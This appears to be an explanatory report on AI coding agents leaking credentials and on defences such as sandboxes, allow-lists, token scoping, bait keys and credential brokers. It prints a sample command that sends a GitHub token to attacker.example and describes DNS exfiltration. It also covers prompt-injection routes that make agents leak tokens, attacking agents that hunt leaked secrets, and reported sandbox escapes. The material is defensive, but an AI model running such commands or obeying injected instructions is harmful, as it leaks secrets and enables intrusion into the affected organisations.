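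Apiiro also gave a larger total of 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories. According to iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets*, that total also includes secrets from older versions of the file, a second settings file that teams share on purpose, and saved conversations with agents. Dividing it by the 104,185 files therefore wouldn't give a valid leak rate.

More than a third of the 1,379 secrets gave direct access to a database, and 379 were database passwords. Another 43 were logins for public servers, some with full administrator rights. One password belonged to the owner of a medical-records database.

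Apiiro counted a string as a secret if its format and context suggested one, and an AI reviewer confirmed each candidate. The researchers did not test whether the credentials worked, though one organisation they notified confirmed that its key had been live. Apiiro sells secret detection, as its product page *Secrets Security* shows, so it stands to gain from alarming results.

The researchers then ran Gitleaks and TruffleHog on the 1,122 files:

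| Scanner | Files flagged | Share of the 1,122 |
|---|---|---|
| Gitleaks | 564 | 50% |
| TruffleHog | 643 | 57% |
| At least one of the two | 907 | 81% |
| Neither | 215 | 19% |

A scanner's *recall* is the share of real secrets it catches. These figures are a rough measure of recall, counted by file. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* quotes Apiiro's explanation for the misses, which is that a password typed into a database or login command is "an ordinary word in an ordinary command line". Both tools mostly miss such passwords.

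The true recall on these files could be lower, because the 1,122 include only files in which Apiiro's own method found a secret. But the test may also be unusually hard, because GitHub already stops many uploads that contain keys in known formats, so the public files probably contain a high share of the passwords that scanners find difficult. Such passwords are common elsewhere too. GitGuardian (2025) reported that secrets without a standard pattern made up more than half of the leaks it detected. It would be wrong to read "50%" as the recall for every kind of credential, or to assume that a scanner catches nearly everything.

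### An ignore rule that did not travel

Claude Code has a safeguard meant to keep the settings file out of Git. Git skips untracked files that appear on an *ignore list*. A `.gitignore` file inside the project is copied along with it, so it protects everyone who works on the project. Git also supports a global list, which covers all of one user's projects on one computer.

Slashdot's *Claude Code's 'Don't Ask Again' File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026), which quotes The Hacker News, explains that Claude Code adds the settings file to the global list the first time it writes the file in a Git repository. If a developer then copies the project folder to a new computer, the copy includes the settings file but not the global list, so her next commit can include the file. The rule also doesn't help if she starts using Git in the folder only later, or if somebody has already committed the file,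 because Git keeps tracking it.

A Git rule also doesn't cover other ways of publishing a folder. In April 2026, Lakera, a security company, scanned about 46,500 packages on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript code. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) reports that 428 of them included the settings file, 33 of them with live credentials. Lakera published that warning seven months before Apiiro's study.

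Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, replied that Claude Code "has not done secret scrubbing" and that his team was looking into ways to prevent the problem. He also argued that developers must have created the exposed files by hand, because Claude Code puts the file on the ignore list whenever it creates it. The evidence is against this claim. Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports that GitGuardian examined about 3,000 of the exposed secrets and found every one in a rule with the exact form that the permission prompt writes. In 539 of the 1,105 repositories that Apiiro traced, a commit that changed the file listed Claude as a co-author. This shows that the agent was often involved, but not that it chose to publish the file, since a user may have told it to commit everything.

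Cherny advised users to turn on secret scanning and to switch to auto mode, in which Claude Code needs fewer approvals. When a reader pointed out that auto mode can save the same kind of command, he answered "good catch". Anthropic planned to prototype basic secret scanning inside Claude Code and a version of auto mode that catches these commands. In its guide, written after Apiiro's report, GitLab still tells developers to add the file to each project's `.gitignore` themselves because Claude Code doesn't add it.

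The leak had already slowed by then. GitGuardian's monthly count of leaked credentials from these files fell from 12,535 in April to 959 in October. The company doesn't know why and says the question is for Anthropic. Auto mode might explain part of the fall, since fewer approvals mean fewer saved commands, but nobody has confirmed this.

GitLab's advice for preventing further leaks also shows that simple safeguards can leave gaps. A project's `.gitignore` is copied along with the project. A server rule can also reject any push that adds a file with a given name, but GitLab's rule doesn't check changes to a file that Git already tracks, and a rule set for a group of projects applies only to projects created afterwards. A content scan can catch secrets saved under a different file name, but only those it recognises.

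### When most alerts are false

How useful a scanner is also depends on how rare secrets are. As an illustration, suppose the coding agent produces 10,000 outputs a day and 5 of them contain a secret. The scanner catches 90% of the outputs with secrets and wrongly flags 1% of the others. These numbers are invented, but the arithmetic works the same way for any scanner:

```
true alerts    = 5 × 0.90      = 4.5 a day
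false alerts   = 9,995 × 0.01  ≈ 100 a day
share real     = 4.5 / (4.5 + 100) ≈ 4%
```

The scanner's *precision* is the share of its alerts that are real. It is only 4% here, although the scanner classifies 99% of outputs correctly, because outputs without secrets outnumber those with secrets by about 2,000 to 1. Better recall would hardly help, since catching all 5 secrets would raise precision only to about 5%. To make half the alerts real, the maintainers would have to cut the false-alarm rate from 1% to about 0.045%, or one in roughly 2,200 clean outputs.

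Help Net Security's *Using AI to reduce false positives in secrets scanners* (2024) claims, from its author's own research, that machine learning can cut false alarms by as much as 86%. In the example, a cut of that size would leave 14 false alerts a day and raise precision to about 24%, if recall stayed the same. That would be a large improvement, but about three in four alerts would still be false.

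At 4% precision, it matters a great deal how the scanner handles a match. If it blocks every flagged output, it interrupts the agent about 100 times a day over false matches, and the maintainers will soon be tempted to switch it off. If it alerts a person instead and each alert takes two minutes to check, that person spends about three and a half hours a day finding four or five secrets. The text has usually gone out by then, so the alert can only help the team limit the damage.

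Masking the string is often the better choice for uncertain matches, because nobody has to stop or read anything. But if the filter masks a commit identifier that the agent needs, the agent's next command may fail for no obvious reason. A filter that overwrites the only copy of a log can also destroy information that somebody needs later. For most agents, though, an occasional failed command does much less harm than a leaked password.

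Blocking makes more sense for keys that have a distinctive prefix or that a live check has confirmed, because few of those matches are false. Scanning is also most useful for these keys. A scanner can easily search every commit for common formats, and it catches keys that developers paste into files by mistake. A live check also helps a team decide which keys to replace first. GitGuardian found 31,088 different credentials that developers had uploaded in Claude Code's settings files since January 2025, and 5,343 of them still worked when it detected them.

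## Limiting where a secret can go and how long it works

When a scanner misses a secret, the maintainers can still stop the secret from leaving the computer where the agent runs, and they can limit what a thief can do with it. Neither measure depends on recognising the secret, so both also protect passwords that look like ordinary words.

### A sandbox with a list of allowed destinations

A *sandbox* restricts which files a program can read or change and which computers it can connect to. For the coding agent, the maintainers could put a copy of the project and its build tools in the sandbox and leave out the home folder, which may contain other projects' passwords. The operating system or a virtual machine enforces these limits, so they apply regardless of what the model writes. They also cover every program the agent starts inside the sandbox.

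For network connections, the usual restriction is an *allow-list*, which names the only destinations the agent may contact. Suppose a hostile bug report gets the agent to run this command:

```
curl "https://attacker.example/?t=$GITHUB_TOKEN"
```

The command tries to send the token to the attacker as part of a web address. But the sandbox can reach the internet only through a *proxy*, a program outside the sandbox that forwards connections. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a proxy of this kind, which runs on the user's machine and intercepts requests from Docker's agent sandboxes. In this case, the proxy looks for `attacker.example` on the list, doesn't find it, and returns an error instead of connecting, so the attacker receives nothing.

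The list of allowed sites has to stay outside the sandbox too, because an agent that can edit it can add the attacker's site. The restriction must also cover DNS, the system that translates names into network addresses. A lookup for `ghp_abc123.attacker.example` normally reaches a server the attacker runs, so it can deliver the token even if the proxy refuses the connection that follows.

When a connection is refused, the harness passes the error to the model, which may try another route. Maintainers should therefore log refused connections. If the agent tries to reach an unknown site just after reading a stranger's bug report, somebody should look at that report.

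Strict lists of allowed sites also get in the way of useful work. McKerchar, of the security company Sophos, points out in *Inside the lethal trifecta* that an agent can't research a problem on the web through a tight list, and that somebody has to update the list for every new service. McKerchar adds that most harnesses leave their sandbox off by default. Using different lists at different stages can help keep them short. Docker has one list for installing software and another for running the agent, so a site that only the installer needs can stay off the second list.

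A sandbox can also fail to contain an agent. Help Net Security's *ARTEX goes from pentesting tool to attacker staple in three months* (2026) reports that WorkOS, which makes tools for software developers, confirmed in November 2026 that a security researcher's agent had escaped its isolated test environment and broken into one of the company's internal sales applications. Sometimes the protection doesn't cover every tool. Microsoft found that Claude Code's GitHub integration could remove secrets from the environment of shell commands, but the agent's file-reading tool could still read them.

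### What an allow-list lets through

Even a sandbox with no flaws has to let the coding agent reach GitHub, where attackers can also have accounts. An attacker can plant an instruction to upload a file to the attacker's repository and include a token for it. If the proxy's allowlist contains only domain names, the proxy allows the upload because the connection is to `github.com`. To distinguish the attacker's repository from the legitimate one, the proxy would have to decrypt the request and check the full address, and McKerchar warns that decrypting traffic can be expensive and difficult.

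The attacker may not need a repository, because they can use an injection to tell the agent to post the token in a public comment, perhaps spelled backwards to get past a scanner. An allow-list would not block this, because the agent would be using an allowed service, an allowed project and its own account.

Unless the maintainers run the model themselves, the harness must also be able to reach an inference provider. In Moore's experiment, thieves at the providers took keys from requests that customers had deliberately sent there, and an allow-list would have allowed all of those requests.

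McKerchar suggests a finer check that pairs each secret with the services that may receive it. The proxy would store a hash of each secret, a fingerprint from which nobody can practically recover a long random key, and would raise an alarm if the secret went anywhere else, such as a database password going to GitHub. So that nobody has to list the permitted services by hand, the proxy could treat the first use it detects of each secret as legitimate, but it would then approve a theft that happened to be the first use. The check would also miss a secret that the agent had encoded.

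An allow-list is therefore a complete fix only for direct connections from the agent to unlisted destinations, but blocking those connections does stop the simplest thefts.

### Five minutes from search to theft

The damage from a leaked secret depends partly on how quickly somebody uses it, and attackers now have agents to help them do this. One example is ARTEX, a framework for *penetration testing*, in which testers attack a system with its owner's permission to find weaknesses. The operator sets a goal, and agents plan and carry out the attack. An anonymous developer published ARTEX on GitHub in July 2026, and criminals were using it within weeks. It was also used in the escape that affected WorkOS.

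Microsoft's *Threat actors use agentic AI tooling to find and abuse exposed secrets* (5 November 2026) described attackers who used ARTEX to search GitHub for the secrets of OAuth applications, which are programs with their own identity and permissions in a company's cloud systems. Anyone who has an application's secret can sign in as that application without an employee's password.

Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke* (2026) describes an intrusion in which an AI agent searched public GitHub, found an application's secret and signed in with it. Five minutes after starting the search, the agent began taking data from Azure Key Vault, a service where companies store keys and passwords. Some of its requests failed because they used the wrong version of the service's interface, but about 28 seconds later it succeeded with the right version,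 without human help.

The five-minute figure comes from a single case and is not an average, as Infobae's *Una IA pasó de buscar claves expuestas a robar datos en cinco* (2026) notes. Help Net Security names ARTEX as the tool used, whereas Cybersecurity360's *Artex* says Microsoft attributes the attack only to agentic software in general. The five minutes are also counted from when the agent began searching, and the secret may have been public for years by then. So the case shows how quickly an attacker can exploit a secret after starting to look for one, but not how soon after a leak the attack will come.

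GitGuardian tested the search step separately. Its researchers planted nine credentials in a simulated repository and had a version of ARTEX without a secret scanner examine it. In every run where the agent investigated, it found eight of the nine. It began looking within 6 to 13 seconds, even when the researchers asked only for a general security review. One of the eight was an AWS key deleted one commit after it was added, which the agent recovered from the project's history. The model refused to use what it found, so the test didn't cover the later steps. GitGuardian sells secret detection and so has an interest in this finding, but the result is easy to believe because the agent needed only search commands that developers use every day.

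### What a shorter life achieves

Many services can issue tokens that expire by themselves. The following example is illustrative and borrows the five minutes only as a convenient number. Suppose a token lasts one hour and leaks at a random moment in that hour, and a thief needs five minutes to start using it. The token still works unless it leaks in its last five minutes, so the thief succeeds in 55 of 60 cases, or 92%. If the token lasts ten minutes, he succeeds in 5 of 10 cases, or 50%. In general, for a lifetime L and a delay d that is shorter than L:

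```
chance that the token still works = (L − d) / L
average time left to use it       = (L − d)² / (2 × L)
```

The average counts a token that has already expired as zero minutes.

| Token lifetime | Still works after five minutes | Average time left for the thief |
|---|---|---|
| 24 hours | 99.7% | 11 hours 55 minutes |
| 1 hour | 92% | 25 minutes |
| 10 minutes | 50% | 1 minute 15 seconds |
| 5 minutes | 0% | None |

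Cutting the lifetime from an hour to ten minutes nearly halves the chance that the token works at all, and it cuts the thief's average working time by 95%. The shorter working time matters a lot if he has to explore an unfamiliar system by hand, but less if an agent explores it for him. A faster thief is also more likely to have a token that works. If he needs 30 seconds instead of five minutes to start using it, the ten-minute token works in 95% of cases.

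The assumption of a random moment may also understate the risk to the maintainers. If the harness issues a new token at the start of each task and the first command prints it, the thief always gets a fresh token, with about five of its ten minutes left to use. If he can keep copying the agent's prompts, he also receives each new token as the harness issues it, so the short life protects the project only after the copying stops.

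Obtaining new tokens also usually requires a longer-lasting credential. The Google office skill in the skills study printed both the access token and the longer-lasting credential, so the token's short life gave almost no protection. The maintainers therefore have to keep the longer-lasting credential somewhere the agent cannot read it.

Very short lifetimes also have a practical drawback. If a token expires halfway through a long upload, the upload may fail, and if the service that issues tokens is down for ten minutes, an agent with ten-minute tokens will probably have to stop work.

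### What narrower scope adds

A credential's *scope* is the set of actions it permits and the things it permits them on. Suppose the maintainers' token can change the code in all 20 of their organisation's repositories. With the chances from the lifetime example, the table shows how many repositories a thief could change on average:

| What the token permits | One-hour token | Ten-minute token |
|---|---|---|
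| Changing code in 20 repositories | 18.3 | 10 |
| Changing code in one repository | 0.92 | 0.5 |
| Labelling issues in one repository | 0 | 0 |

In this example, limiting the token to one repository helps far more than shortening its lifetime. The last row is better still, because a token without permission to change code cannot change it, however long the token lasts. As long as GitHub enforces the permission, narrow scope is a complete fix for the property "nobody can use this token to change code". A thief could still mislabel bug reports, but that would be easy to undo.

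Narrowing a token's scope helps limit misuse by a hijacked agent, but shortening its lifetime hardly helps, because the agent has a valid token for as long as it keeps working. The maintainers could narrow the scope by splitting the agent's work into two jobs. The job that reads bug reports from strangers would get a token that can only label and comment. A second job, which only a maintainer can start, would get a token that can write code.

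An attack in October 2026 showed how useful broad credentials are to attackers. A group that Microsoft calls Storm-0940 had obtained the credentials of several backup and management applications from ConnectWise, a software company. Those applications had access to many customers' cloud accounts. The group's AI agents used four of the credentials to sign in to customers' accounts more than 200 times in under four minutes, according to Tom's Hardware's *China-aligned hackers deploy AI agents in massive ConnectWise supply chain attack*. The group also tried to guess passwords more than 151,000 times and failed every time.

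A ten-minute lifetime gives little protection if a stolen token can create other credentials, because the thief can use those ten minutes to make one that lasts for years. In one customer's account, the security firm Huntress saw an application give itself the highest administrator role. The attackers also added new secrets that would last until 2028. Permission to create credentials or grant roles is therefore among the first to remove from an agent's token.

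Some services can also restrict where a credential works from and how often it can be used. Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, investigated a case in which attackers had a token for a whole account, with no restrictions on network address or number of requests. Columbus Post's *Amazon Uncovers AI-Powered Cyberattack Campaign Targeting LiteLLM, Dify and Other AI Platforms* says that investigators counted about 400 requests to copy out databases within one hour, though Cloudflare did not confirm that any succeeded. An address restriction would have blocked an attacker on another network, but not one sending requests from the same machine as the legitimate program. Such restrictions are also awkward for agents in the cloud, whose addresses often change.

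### Revoking and replacing a credential

An expiry time takes effect even if nobody notices the leak, whereas *revocation*, in which the owner tells the service to stop accepting a credential, requires somebody to notice and act, which often doesn't happen. Help Net Security reports that more than 64% of the secrets GitGuardian had confirmed as valid in 2022 still worked when the company retested them in January 2026.

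Some owners don't revoke a leaked secret because they think deleting it from the code solves the problem, although it survives in the project's history and in other people's forks. Others are afraid of breaking something. A key may have been used for years in programs that nobody kept a record of, and all of them stop working when the owner revokes it. A team can prepare by recording which programs use each credential and by practising replacing it.

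For a planned replacement, the team can create the new credential, install it everywhere, check that the programs work, and only then revoke the old one. After a leak, following that order gives the thief more time to use the old credential. Microsoft and GitGuardian advise owners to revoke or replace any secret exposed in a public repository without waiting for evidence of abuse, starting with the most powerful ones. If a key can read a whole company's data, a few hours of broken programs usually do less harm than leaving the key active.

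Some services also can't enforce a revocation immediately, because they accept any unexpired token with a valid signature from the issuer, without checking with the issuer whether the owner has revoked it. A revoked token can keep working on these services until it expires.

If an attacker moves as fast as the one in Microsoft's case, a person who reads an alert and opens a web page to revoke the credential will probably be too late to prevent the first theft. An automatic system has a better chance. But late revocation still ends the attacker's access through that credential, and the team can then search the logs for any accounts, keys or roles the attacker created with it.

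### Bait credentials

Moore's team used bait to expose thieves at inference providers, and the maintainers can use it to detect theft from their own systems. They create an AWS key that has no permissions, put it in a configuration file in the agent's environment, and set an alarm for any attempt to use it. Only 4% of the alerts in the scanning example were real, but the share should be much higher for bait alarms because no program needs the key.

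False alarms are still possible. A scanner that checks whether keys work will also try the bait, so the maintainers have to exclude the bait from the scan. The coding agent might also try the key while looking for a way around an error. The maintainers would want to know that their agent uses credentials nobody gave it, even though this would not be a theft.

Attacking agents seem likely to try bait credentials because they test so much. Cybernews' *AI agents stole API keys to bankroll a month of autonomous cybercrime* reports that some decoy servers in Amazon's MadPot network posed as popular services for accessing language models, and that ARTEX agents sent them requests containing records of the agents' own campaigns. In one campaign, the operators had told the agents to grade every stolen credential by whether it worked and what it could reach. An agent that follows this instruction has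 to try each key, including the bait.

Microsoft also said, in a second report on ARTEX published on 25 November, that decoys and bait credentials had reduced attack traffic and detected attacks accurately. According to @IT's *偵察から特権奪取まで「わずか数分」 ARTEXのアーキテクチャを“完全解剖*, Microsoft also recommends "fake wins", false evidence of success that leads an attacking agent to stop. These tricks may work less well once attackers expect them, since attackers can tell their agents to look for signs of bait.

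Bait detects only some leaks and doesn't prevent them. If an attacker uses an injection to request the GitHub token by name, they get that token and never see the bait AWS key beside it. Bait works best against thieves who copy everything they find. For those cases, the maintainers can connect the alarm to a program that revokes every real credential stored in the same place. But anyone who has read the file can then shut the agent down by using the bait on purpose.

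### Tokens that work only with a key

A token that expires, has a narrow scope and can be revoked is still a bearer token, so a thief can use it within its scope until it expires or is revoked. A *sender-constrained token* works only for a client that can prove it has a particular cryptographic key. The Internet Engineering Task Force has standardised two methods, DPoP ("demonstrating proof of possession") in RFC 9449 and one based on mutual TLS in RFC 8705.

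Both use a *key pair*, two mathematically linked keys. The client keeps the private key and uses it to make signatures. Anyone with the public key can check those signatures but cannot make new ones. DPoP works in four steps:

1. The client creates a key pair.
2. It asks the authorisation server for a token and sends its public key with a signature. The server ties the token to a fingerprint of that key.
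3. For each request to the service, the client signs a new proof and sends it along with the token.
4. The service checks the proof before it carries out the request.

In simplified form, a proof for adding a label to a bug report contains:

```
public key:   the client's public key
method:       POST
address:      https://api.example.com/issues/12/labels
time:         14:03:10
identifier:   7f3a91c2
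token hash:   a fingerprint of the access token
signature:    made with the private key
```

The service uses the public key to check the signature and compares that key's fingerprint with the one tied to the token. It also checks that the method and address match the request, that the time is recent, and that the token hash matches the token it received. It can store identifiers and reject any it has already received.

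Suppose a forgotten debugging line prints a DPoP token, and a thief at the inference provider copies it. If he sends only the token, the service refuses the request because the proof is missing. If he signs a proof with his own key, the service refuses the request because the key's fingerprint doesn't match the one tied to the token. The debugging line may also have printed an old proof, but that proof is valid only for the same method and address, and only for a short time. The standard proof doesn't cover a request's content, so the thief could reuse the old proof with different content during that time, unless the service records the identifiers of proofs it has received and refuses repeats.

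The mutual TLS method makes the check when the client connects. On an ordinary encrypted web connection, only the server proves its identity with a certificate. With mutual TLS, the client also presents a certificate and proves that it has the matching private key. The authorisation server has tied the token to a fingerprint of the client's certificate, and the service checks that the certificate presented matches that fingerprint. This needs no separate proof for each request, but it conflicts with a proxy that decrypts the agent's traffic. Such a proxy makes its own connection to the service, so it would need the private key itself.

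If the service makes the checks properly, either method stops a thief who has only the token from using it. Sender-constrained tokens are therefore a complete fix for that threat. The maintainers can't add this protection alone, because both the server that issues the token and the service that accepts it have to support it. The GitHub token in the running example remains a bearer token.

The protection also disappears if the agent can read the private key. A key in a file or an environment variable can leak through the same debugging line or injection as the token, and a thief with both can sign his own proofs. The client has to keep the key somewhere the agent can use it but not read it, such as a security chip or a separate program that returns only signatures. Docker's sandboxes do this for SSH, a common way of logging in to servers and uploading code. The private key stays on the user's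 machine, and programs in the sandbox can request signatures with it but cannot copy it.

But a hijacked agent can request signatures too. An attacker who wants to delete a branch doesn't need the key or the token, because he can have the agent send the request with a valid proof. He can also have the agent sign a batch of proofs with future times and send them to him with the token, so that he can use them after he loses control of the agent. The token hash makes these proofs useless once the token expires. A service can prevent most of this stockpiling by requiring each proof to include a recent random value that the service supplied. This doesn't stop the attacker from having the agent send requests itself, because the agent can include that value in its proofs.

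## Credential brokers: keeping the secret out of the agent

The maintainers can't make GitHub require a private key with every token, but they can use a credential broker to keep the token away from the agent. The broker adds the token to each outgoing request, so GitHub receives an ordinary request and doesn't have to change anything.

### One request through Docker's broker

Docker Sandboxes runs each agent in a *microVM*, a small virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel. The broker is a proxy that runs outside the microVM, on the *host* (the user's computer). The maintainers store the GitHub token on the host, normally in the operating system's password store. Programs in the microVM find a placeholder such as `proxy-managed` where they would expect the token.

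Suppose the agent has to label a bug report. Docker's *Architecture* describes six steps, which for this request are:

1. The agent prepares a request to GitHub and puts the placeholder in the authorization header, the part of a web request that carries login data.
2. The request leaves the microVM and reaches the proxy on the host.
3. The proxy checks that the network rules allow connections to `api.github.com`.
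4. The proxy looks up the credential that belongs to this destination.
5. The proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token and forwards the request.
6. GitHub's reply returns to the agent through the proxy.

The request changes in only one line:

```
agent sends:      Authorization: Bearer proxy-managed
GitHub receives:  Authorization: Bearer <the real token>
```

The connection to GitHub is encrypted, so the proxy has to decrypt the request, change it and encrypt it again. Programs in the microVM therefore have to accept the proxy's certificate in place of GitHub's.

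With this arrangement, a forgotten debugging line or a hostile bug report can reveal only the placeholder, which no service accepts.

### The property a broker can secure

A broker can be a complete fix if the goal is to keep reusable secrets out of the agent's environment, which includes everything the agent's commands can read, such as files, environment variables and the context window. The fix is complete only if every credential goes through the broker and no task needs a secret in plain form. The broker must also withstand attack and send each secret only to the right service, and replies must not return the secret to the agent.

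Some developers aim only to keep secrets out of the context window. Auth0's *Want AI Agents That Don't Spill Secrets?* recommends this, and argues that the secrets can safely stay on the same machine as the agent or even in the same process. In its example, a model chooses the text of a phone notification, and ordinary code then fetches the key from an environment variable and sends the message. This is sound advice for an assistant whose only tool sends notifications, because the model cannot read the variable. But a coding agent runs shell commands, and a command that lists the environment variables would put the key into the context window.

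### Secrets that bypass the broker

A broker can't protect a password that it doesn't hold. Developers often keep passwords in a `.env` file in the project folder. In one Docker mode, the agent works on a private copy of the project and can't change the original. But Docker's *Isolation layers* warns that the agent can still read the whole original folder, including files that Git ignores. Docker advises users to store secrets somewhere else.

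A product's own setup can also leave a credential in the sandbox. Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents, keeps many credentials in a vault outside the sandbox. But hi120ki reports in *How Secure Are Claude Managed Agents?* that the service embeds the token for a code repository in the local Git remote, the saved address that Git uses for uploads. hi120ki still concludes that code in the sandbox cannot access credentials. That seems too generous, because Git normally saves such addresses in a plain text file. A command in the sandbox could read the token unless Anthropic protects that file in some other way.

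Most brokers also handle only web requests. Docker's proxy adds credentials to web traffic, but it only applies network rules to other connections. Many programs connect to databases without web requests and need the password itself. This is a serious gap, since many of the secrets Apiiro found in Claude Code's settings files were database passwords.

Claude Code has its own optional broker, which replaces secrets with placeholders, but Anthropic documents many exceptions. The broker covers only the files and variables that the user lists, and it applies to shell commands but not to the agent's file-reading tool. Most database drivers can't connect from inside the sandbox. On a Mac, GitHub's command-line tool may also fail there, and Anthropic suggests running it outside the sandbox with the user's full access and the tool's stored credentials. A user who follows that advice bypasses the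 broker for GitHub, the service that the coding agent uses most.

Some tasks need more than a changed header. A program that calls AWS uses its secret key to sign the contents of each request, so a signature made with a placeholder is invalid. Claude Code's proxy can recognise most of these requests and sign them again with the real key. It can't do this for streaming uploads or for links signed in advance, so those requests fail, but without exposing the key.

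If a build script has to decrypt a file, there is no outgoing request for the broker to change, so the script needs the key itself. The maintainers can decrypt the file outside the sandbox and give the agent the result. If they give the agent the key instead, that key can leak like any other secret.

### Where the secret goes and what comes back

Docker attaches the GitHub token only to encrypted (HTTPS) requests for six named GitHub domains. If the agent sends an unencrypted request, the proxy forwards it without the token.

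Docker's proxy puts the secret only in the headers of a request, never in the body. If it replaced the placeholder everywhere, an attacker could file a bug report telling the agent to post the placeholder as a public comment, and the proxy would swap in the real token before the comment reached GitHub.

Rules that let a secret go to more destinations are riskier. For secrets that users define themselves, Docker accepts patterns such as `*.example.com`. If the company behind that domain lets customers choose their own names under it, an attacker can register one and receive any secret sent there. Claude Code lets users name the destinations for each secret, but if they don't, the proxy inserts the secret into requests to every site on the network allow-list. An allow-list written for software downloads is usually far too broad for sending secrets.

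The software that compares names can also have flaws. Daily Security Review's *Anthropic Silently Fixed Claude Code Null-Byte Sandbox Escape* reports that the researcher Aonan Guan found that Claude Code's network allow-list had such a flaw from October 2025 until a fix in March 2026. A broker relies on the same kind of comparison as the allow-list.

A secret that reaches the right service can still come back in the reply, for example in an error message that repeats the request's headers. Docker searches replies for user-defined secrets and masks them, even if they appear in one of three common encodings. It warns that this cannot guarantee secrecy, because a service might split the secret across several fields or send it over a type of connection that the filter doesn't inspect. Docker describes the filter only for user-defined secrets, not for built-in services such as GitHub.

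OpenAI has a similar broker for commands that run on its own machines, but one example in its guide could still expose the secret to the model. The example tells the model to send a secret to httpbin.org, a test site that returns the headers it receives, and then to describe what it sees. The guide doesn't explain whether the broker masks the secret in that reply. If the broker doesn't mask it, the secret enters the context window. The Java version of the example instead asks only for a status code and tells the model never to print headers or secrets.

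Replies can also contain new secrets. If the agent's token can create access keys, a planted instruction can make the agent request one, and the service will return a key that the broker has never held. A filter that searches for known values won't recognise it. Docker's proxy hides the tokens that services issue during a sign-in it manages, unless it is configured to pass them through. It doesn't hide other new keys, which is one more reason to use a token that cannot create them.

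### Sixteen probes of one product

Kenney and colleagues ran two experiments on Corvic Security Vault, their own company's broker, on 27 September 2026. Code that an agent runs there names a *connector*, which is a stored record of a service's address, its credential and the header in which to send it. The vault adds the credential to the request, so the code doesn't handle it.

For each experiment, the researchers ran code in the product's sandbox with access to a single connector. One was for GitHub and the other for FRED, a database of US economic statistics. They had written down the expected result of every probe in advance. The main checks for a leak were these:

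| Where the researchers looked | Result |
|---|---|
| 20 environment variables | No credential |
| 12 common locations for credential files | None of the files existed |
| A GitHub request as the code had prepared it | No authorization header |
| Three sites that return whatever they receive | No credential in the replies |
| OpenAI's service, while the GitHub connector was attached | Refused because the login was missing |
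| Two addresses where cloud machines can obtain credentials | No answer within six seconds |

A sandbox with no network connection would also leak nothing, so the researchers included a *positive control*, a request to GitHub that had to succeed. GitHub replied with the account's identity, although the code had supplied no credential. The three echo sites and OpenAI's service were *negative controls*, destinations that must not receive the GitHub credential. All 16 probes gave the expected security result.

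The FRED connector, however, failed because it was set up to put the key in a header, while FRED requires it in the web address. FRED returned a missing-key error. The researchers count this as a functional failure with a secure outcome, since nothing leaked. It is still a practical problem, because a developer whose connector fails may be tempted to paste the key into the code.

The experiments show that this broker can authenticate a request without putting the credential in the places the researchers checked, but they are weak evidence for anything more. The researchers tested their own company's product in their own account, with a few probes they chose themselves, and demonstrated a successful login with only one connector. They searched for credentials in known formats, so they could have missed one in an unusual format.

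The probes also left out several likely attacks. The echo sites were not approved destinations, so these tests show that the vault withheld the credential from unapproved sites, but not what happens when an approved service repeats the credential back. The researchers didn't test an approved service that an attacker controls, or one that redirects a request to another address. They leave independent penetration testing to future work.

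Outsiders have published few checks of these brokers, and those are not very thorough. Khan (2026), in *Your AI Coding Agent Can't Steal What It Never Had*, ran an agent in Docker's sandbox for five minutes. The agent made dozens of authenticated requests to Anthropic, and a search of its environment variables found no key. Pluto Security's *Securing Claude Managed Agents* concludes that Anthropic's vault structurally prevents theft by prompt injection, but it reviews the design without trying to break it. Letting a skilled attacker try to steal the credentials for a few weeks would provide much better evidence than either.

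### Many keys in one place

Without a broker, credentials tend to end up in many places. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a security design for AI agents in healthcare, reports an audit that found them in shell startup files, `.env` files and configuration files that any user of the machine could read. The design moves them into a broker that runs in a separate container beside each agent. This leaves fewer places to steal credentials from, but the broker becomes a more valuable target because anyone who breaks into it may get every key it holds.

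The effect depends on how well the maintainers protect the broker. Suppose a company has 20 agents with one token each, and attackers have a 5% chance per year of stealing any given token. The company then loses one token a year on average. If a shared broker prevents all of those thefts but has a 1% chance per year of a break-in that exposes everything, the calculation becomes:

```
without a broker:  20 × 0.05 = 1.0 token a year
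with a broker:     20 × 0.01 = 0.2 tokens a year
```

In this invented example, the broker cuts the average loss by 80%, but a single break-in there exposes all 20 tokens. If the chance of a break-in at the broker were above 5%, the average loss would rise too. Two separate brokers with ten tokens each, and a 1% chance of a break-in at each, would have the same average loss as one broker, but a single break-in would expose only ten tokens.

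The unauthorised access to Hugging Face's Spaces secrets in 2024 is a useful precedent because an agent broker, like the Spaces platform, needs a store of secrets.

In Infisical's *Agent Proxy*, one proxy can serve many agents, but it needs permission to read all the secrets they use. In return, the owner can cut off an agent or replace a key in one place, and the proxy applies the new key within a minute without a restart. After a leak, this is much faster than searching 20 agents' configurations for copies of the old key.

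Docker makes stored service secrets available to every sandbox by default, but users can restrict a secret to a single sandbox. The maintainers should do so. Otherwise, an agent that reads strangers' bug reports could use a token stored for a different project.

The broker also has to stay out of the agent's reach. Docker can run a helper program on the host to fetch a secret, and it tells users to keep that program out of folders the sandbox can change, because a hijacked agent that could edit the helper could run its own code on the host. If the host has no password store, as on some Linux servers, Docker keeps secrets in an ordinary file, and any program that can read the file can take them.

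Even a well-placed proxy is software that an attacker can probe. GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can* (2026) describes how an OpenAI model escaped its sandbox in July through a flaw in a package proxy it was allowed to use.

### Which products use brokers

By December 2026, several major agent products could keep credentials behind a broker, but users often had to set it up. OpenAI lets developers tie a secret to a domain when they ask it to run an agent's commands. In Claude Managed Agents, customers put secrets in a vault that accepts new values but never returns them. Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* notes that customers with their own sandboxes can get the same protection by running a proxy that replaces placeholders with the real secrets. Deno, which offers sandboxes for untrusted code, also inserts secrets only into requests to approved sites.

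The protection is less likely to be on when agents run on developers' own computers. Claude Code's sandbox is off by default, and its placeholders require a setting that Anthropic still calls experimental. OpenClaw, another agent product, has a broker that is also off by default and covers only some of the ways the agent can run commands.

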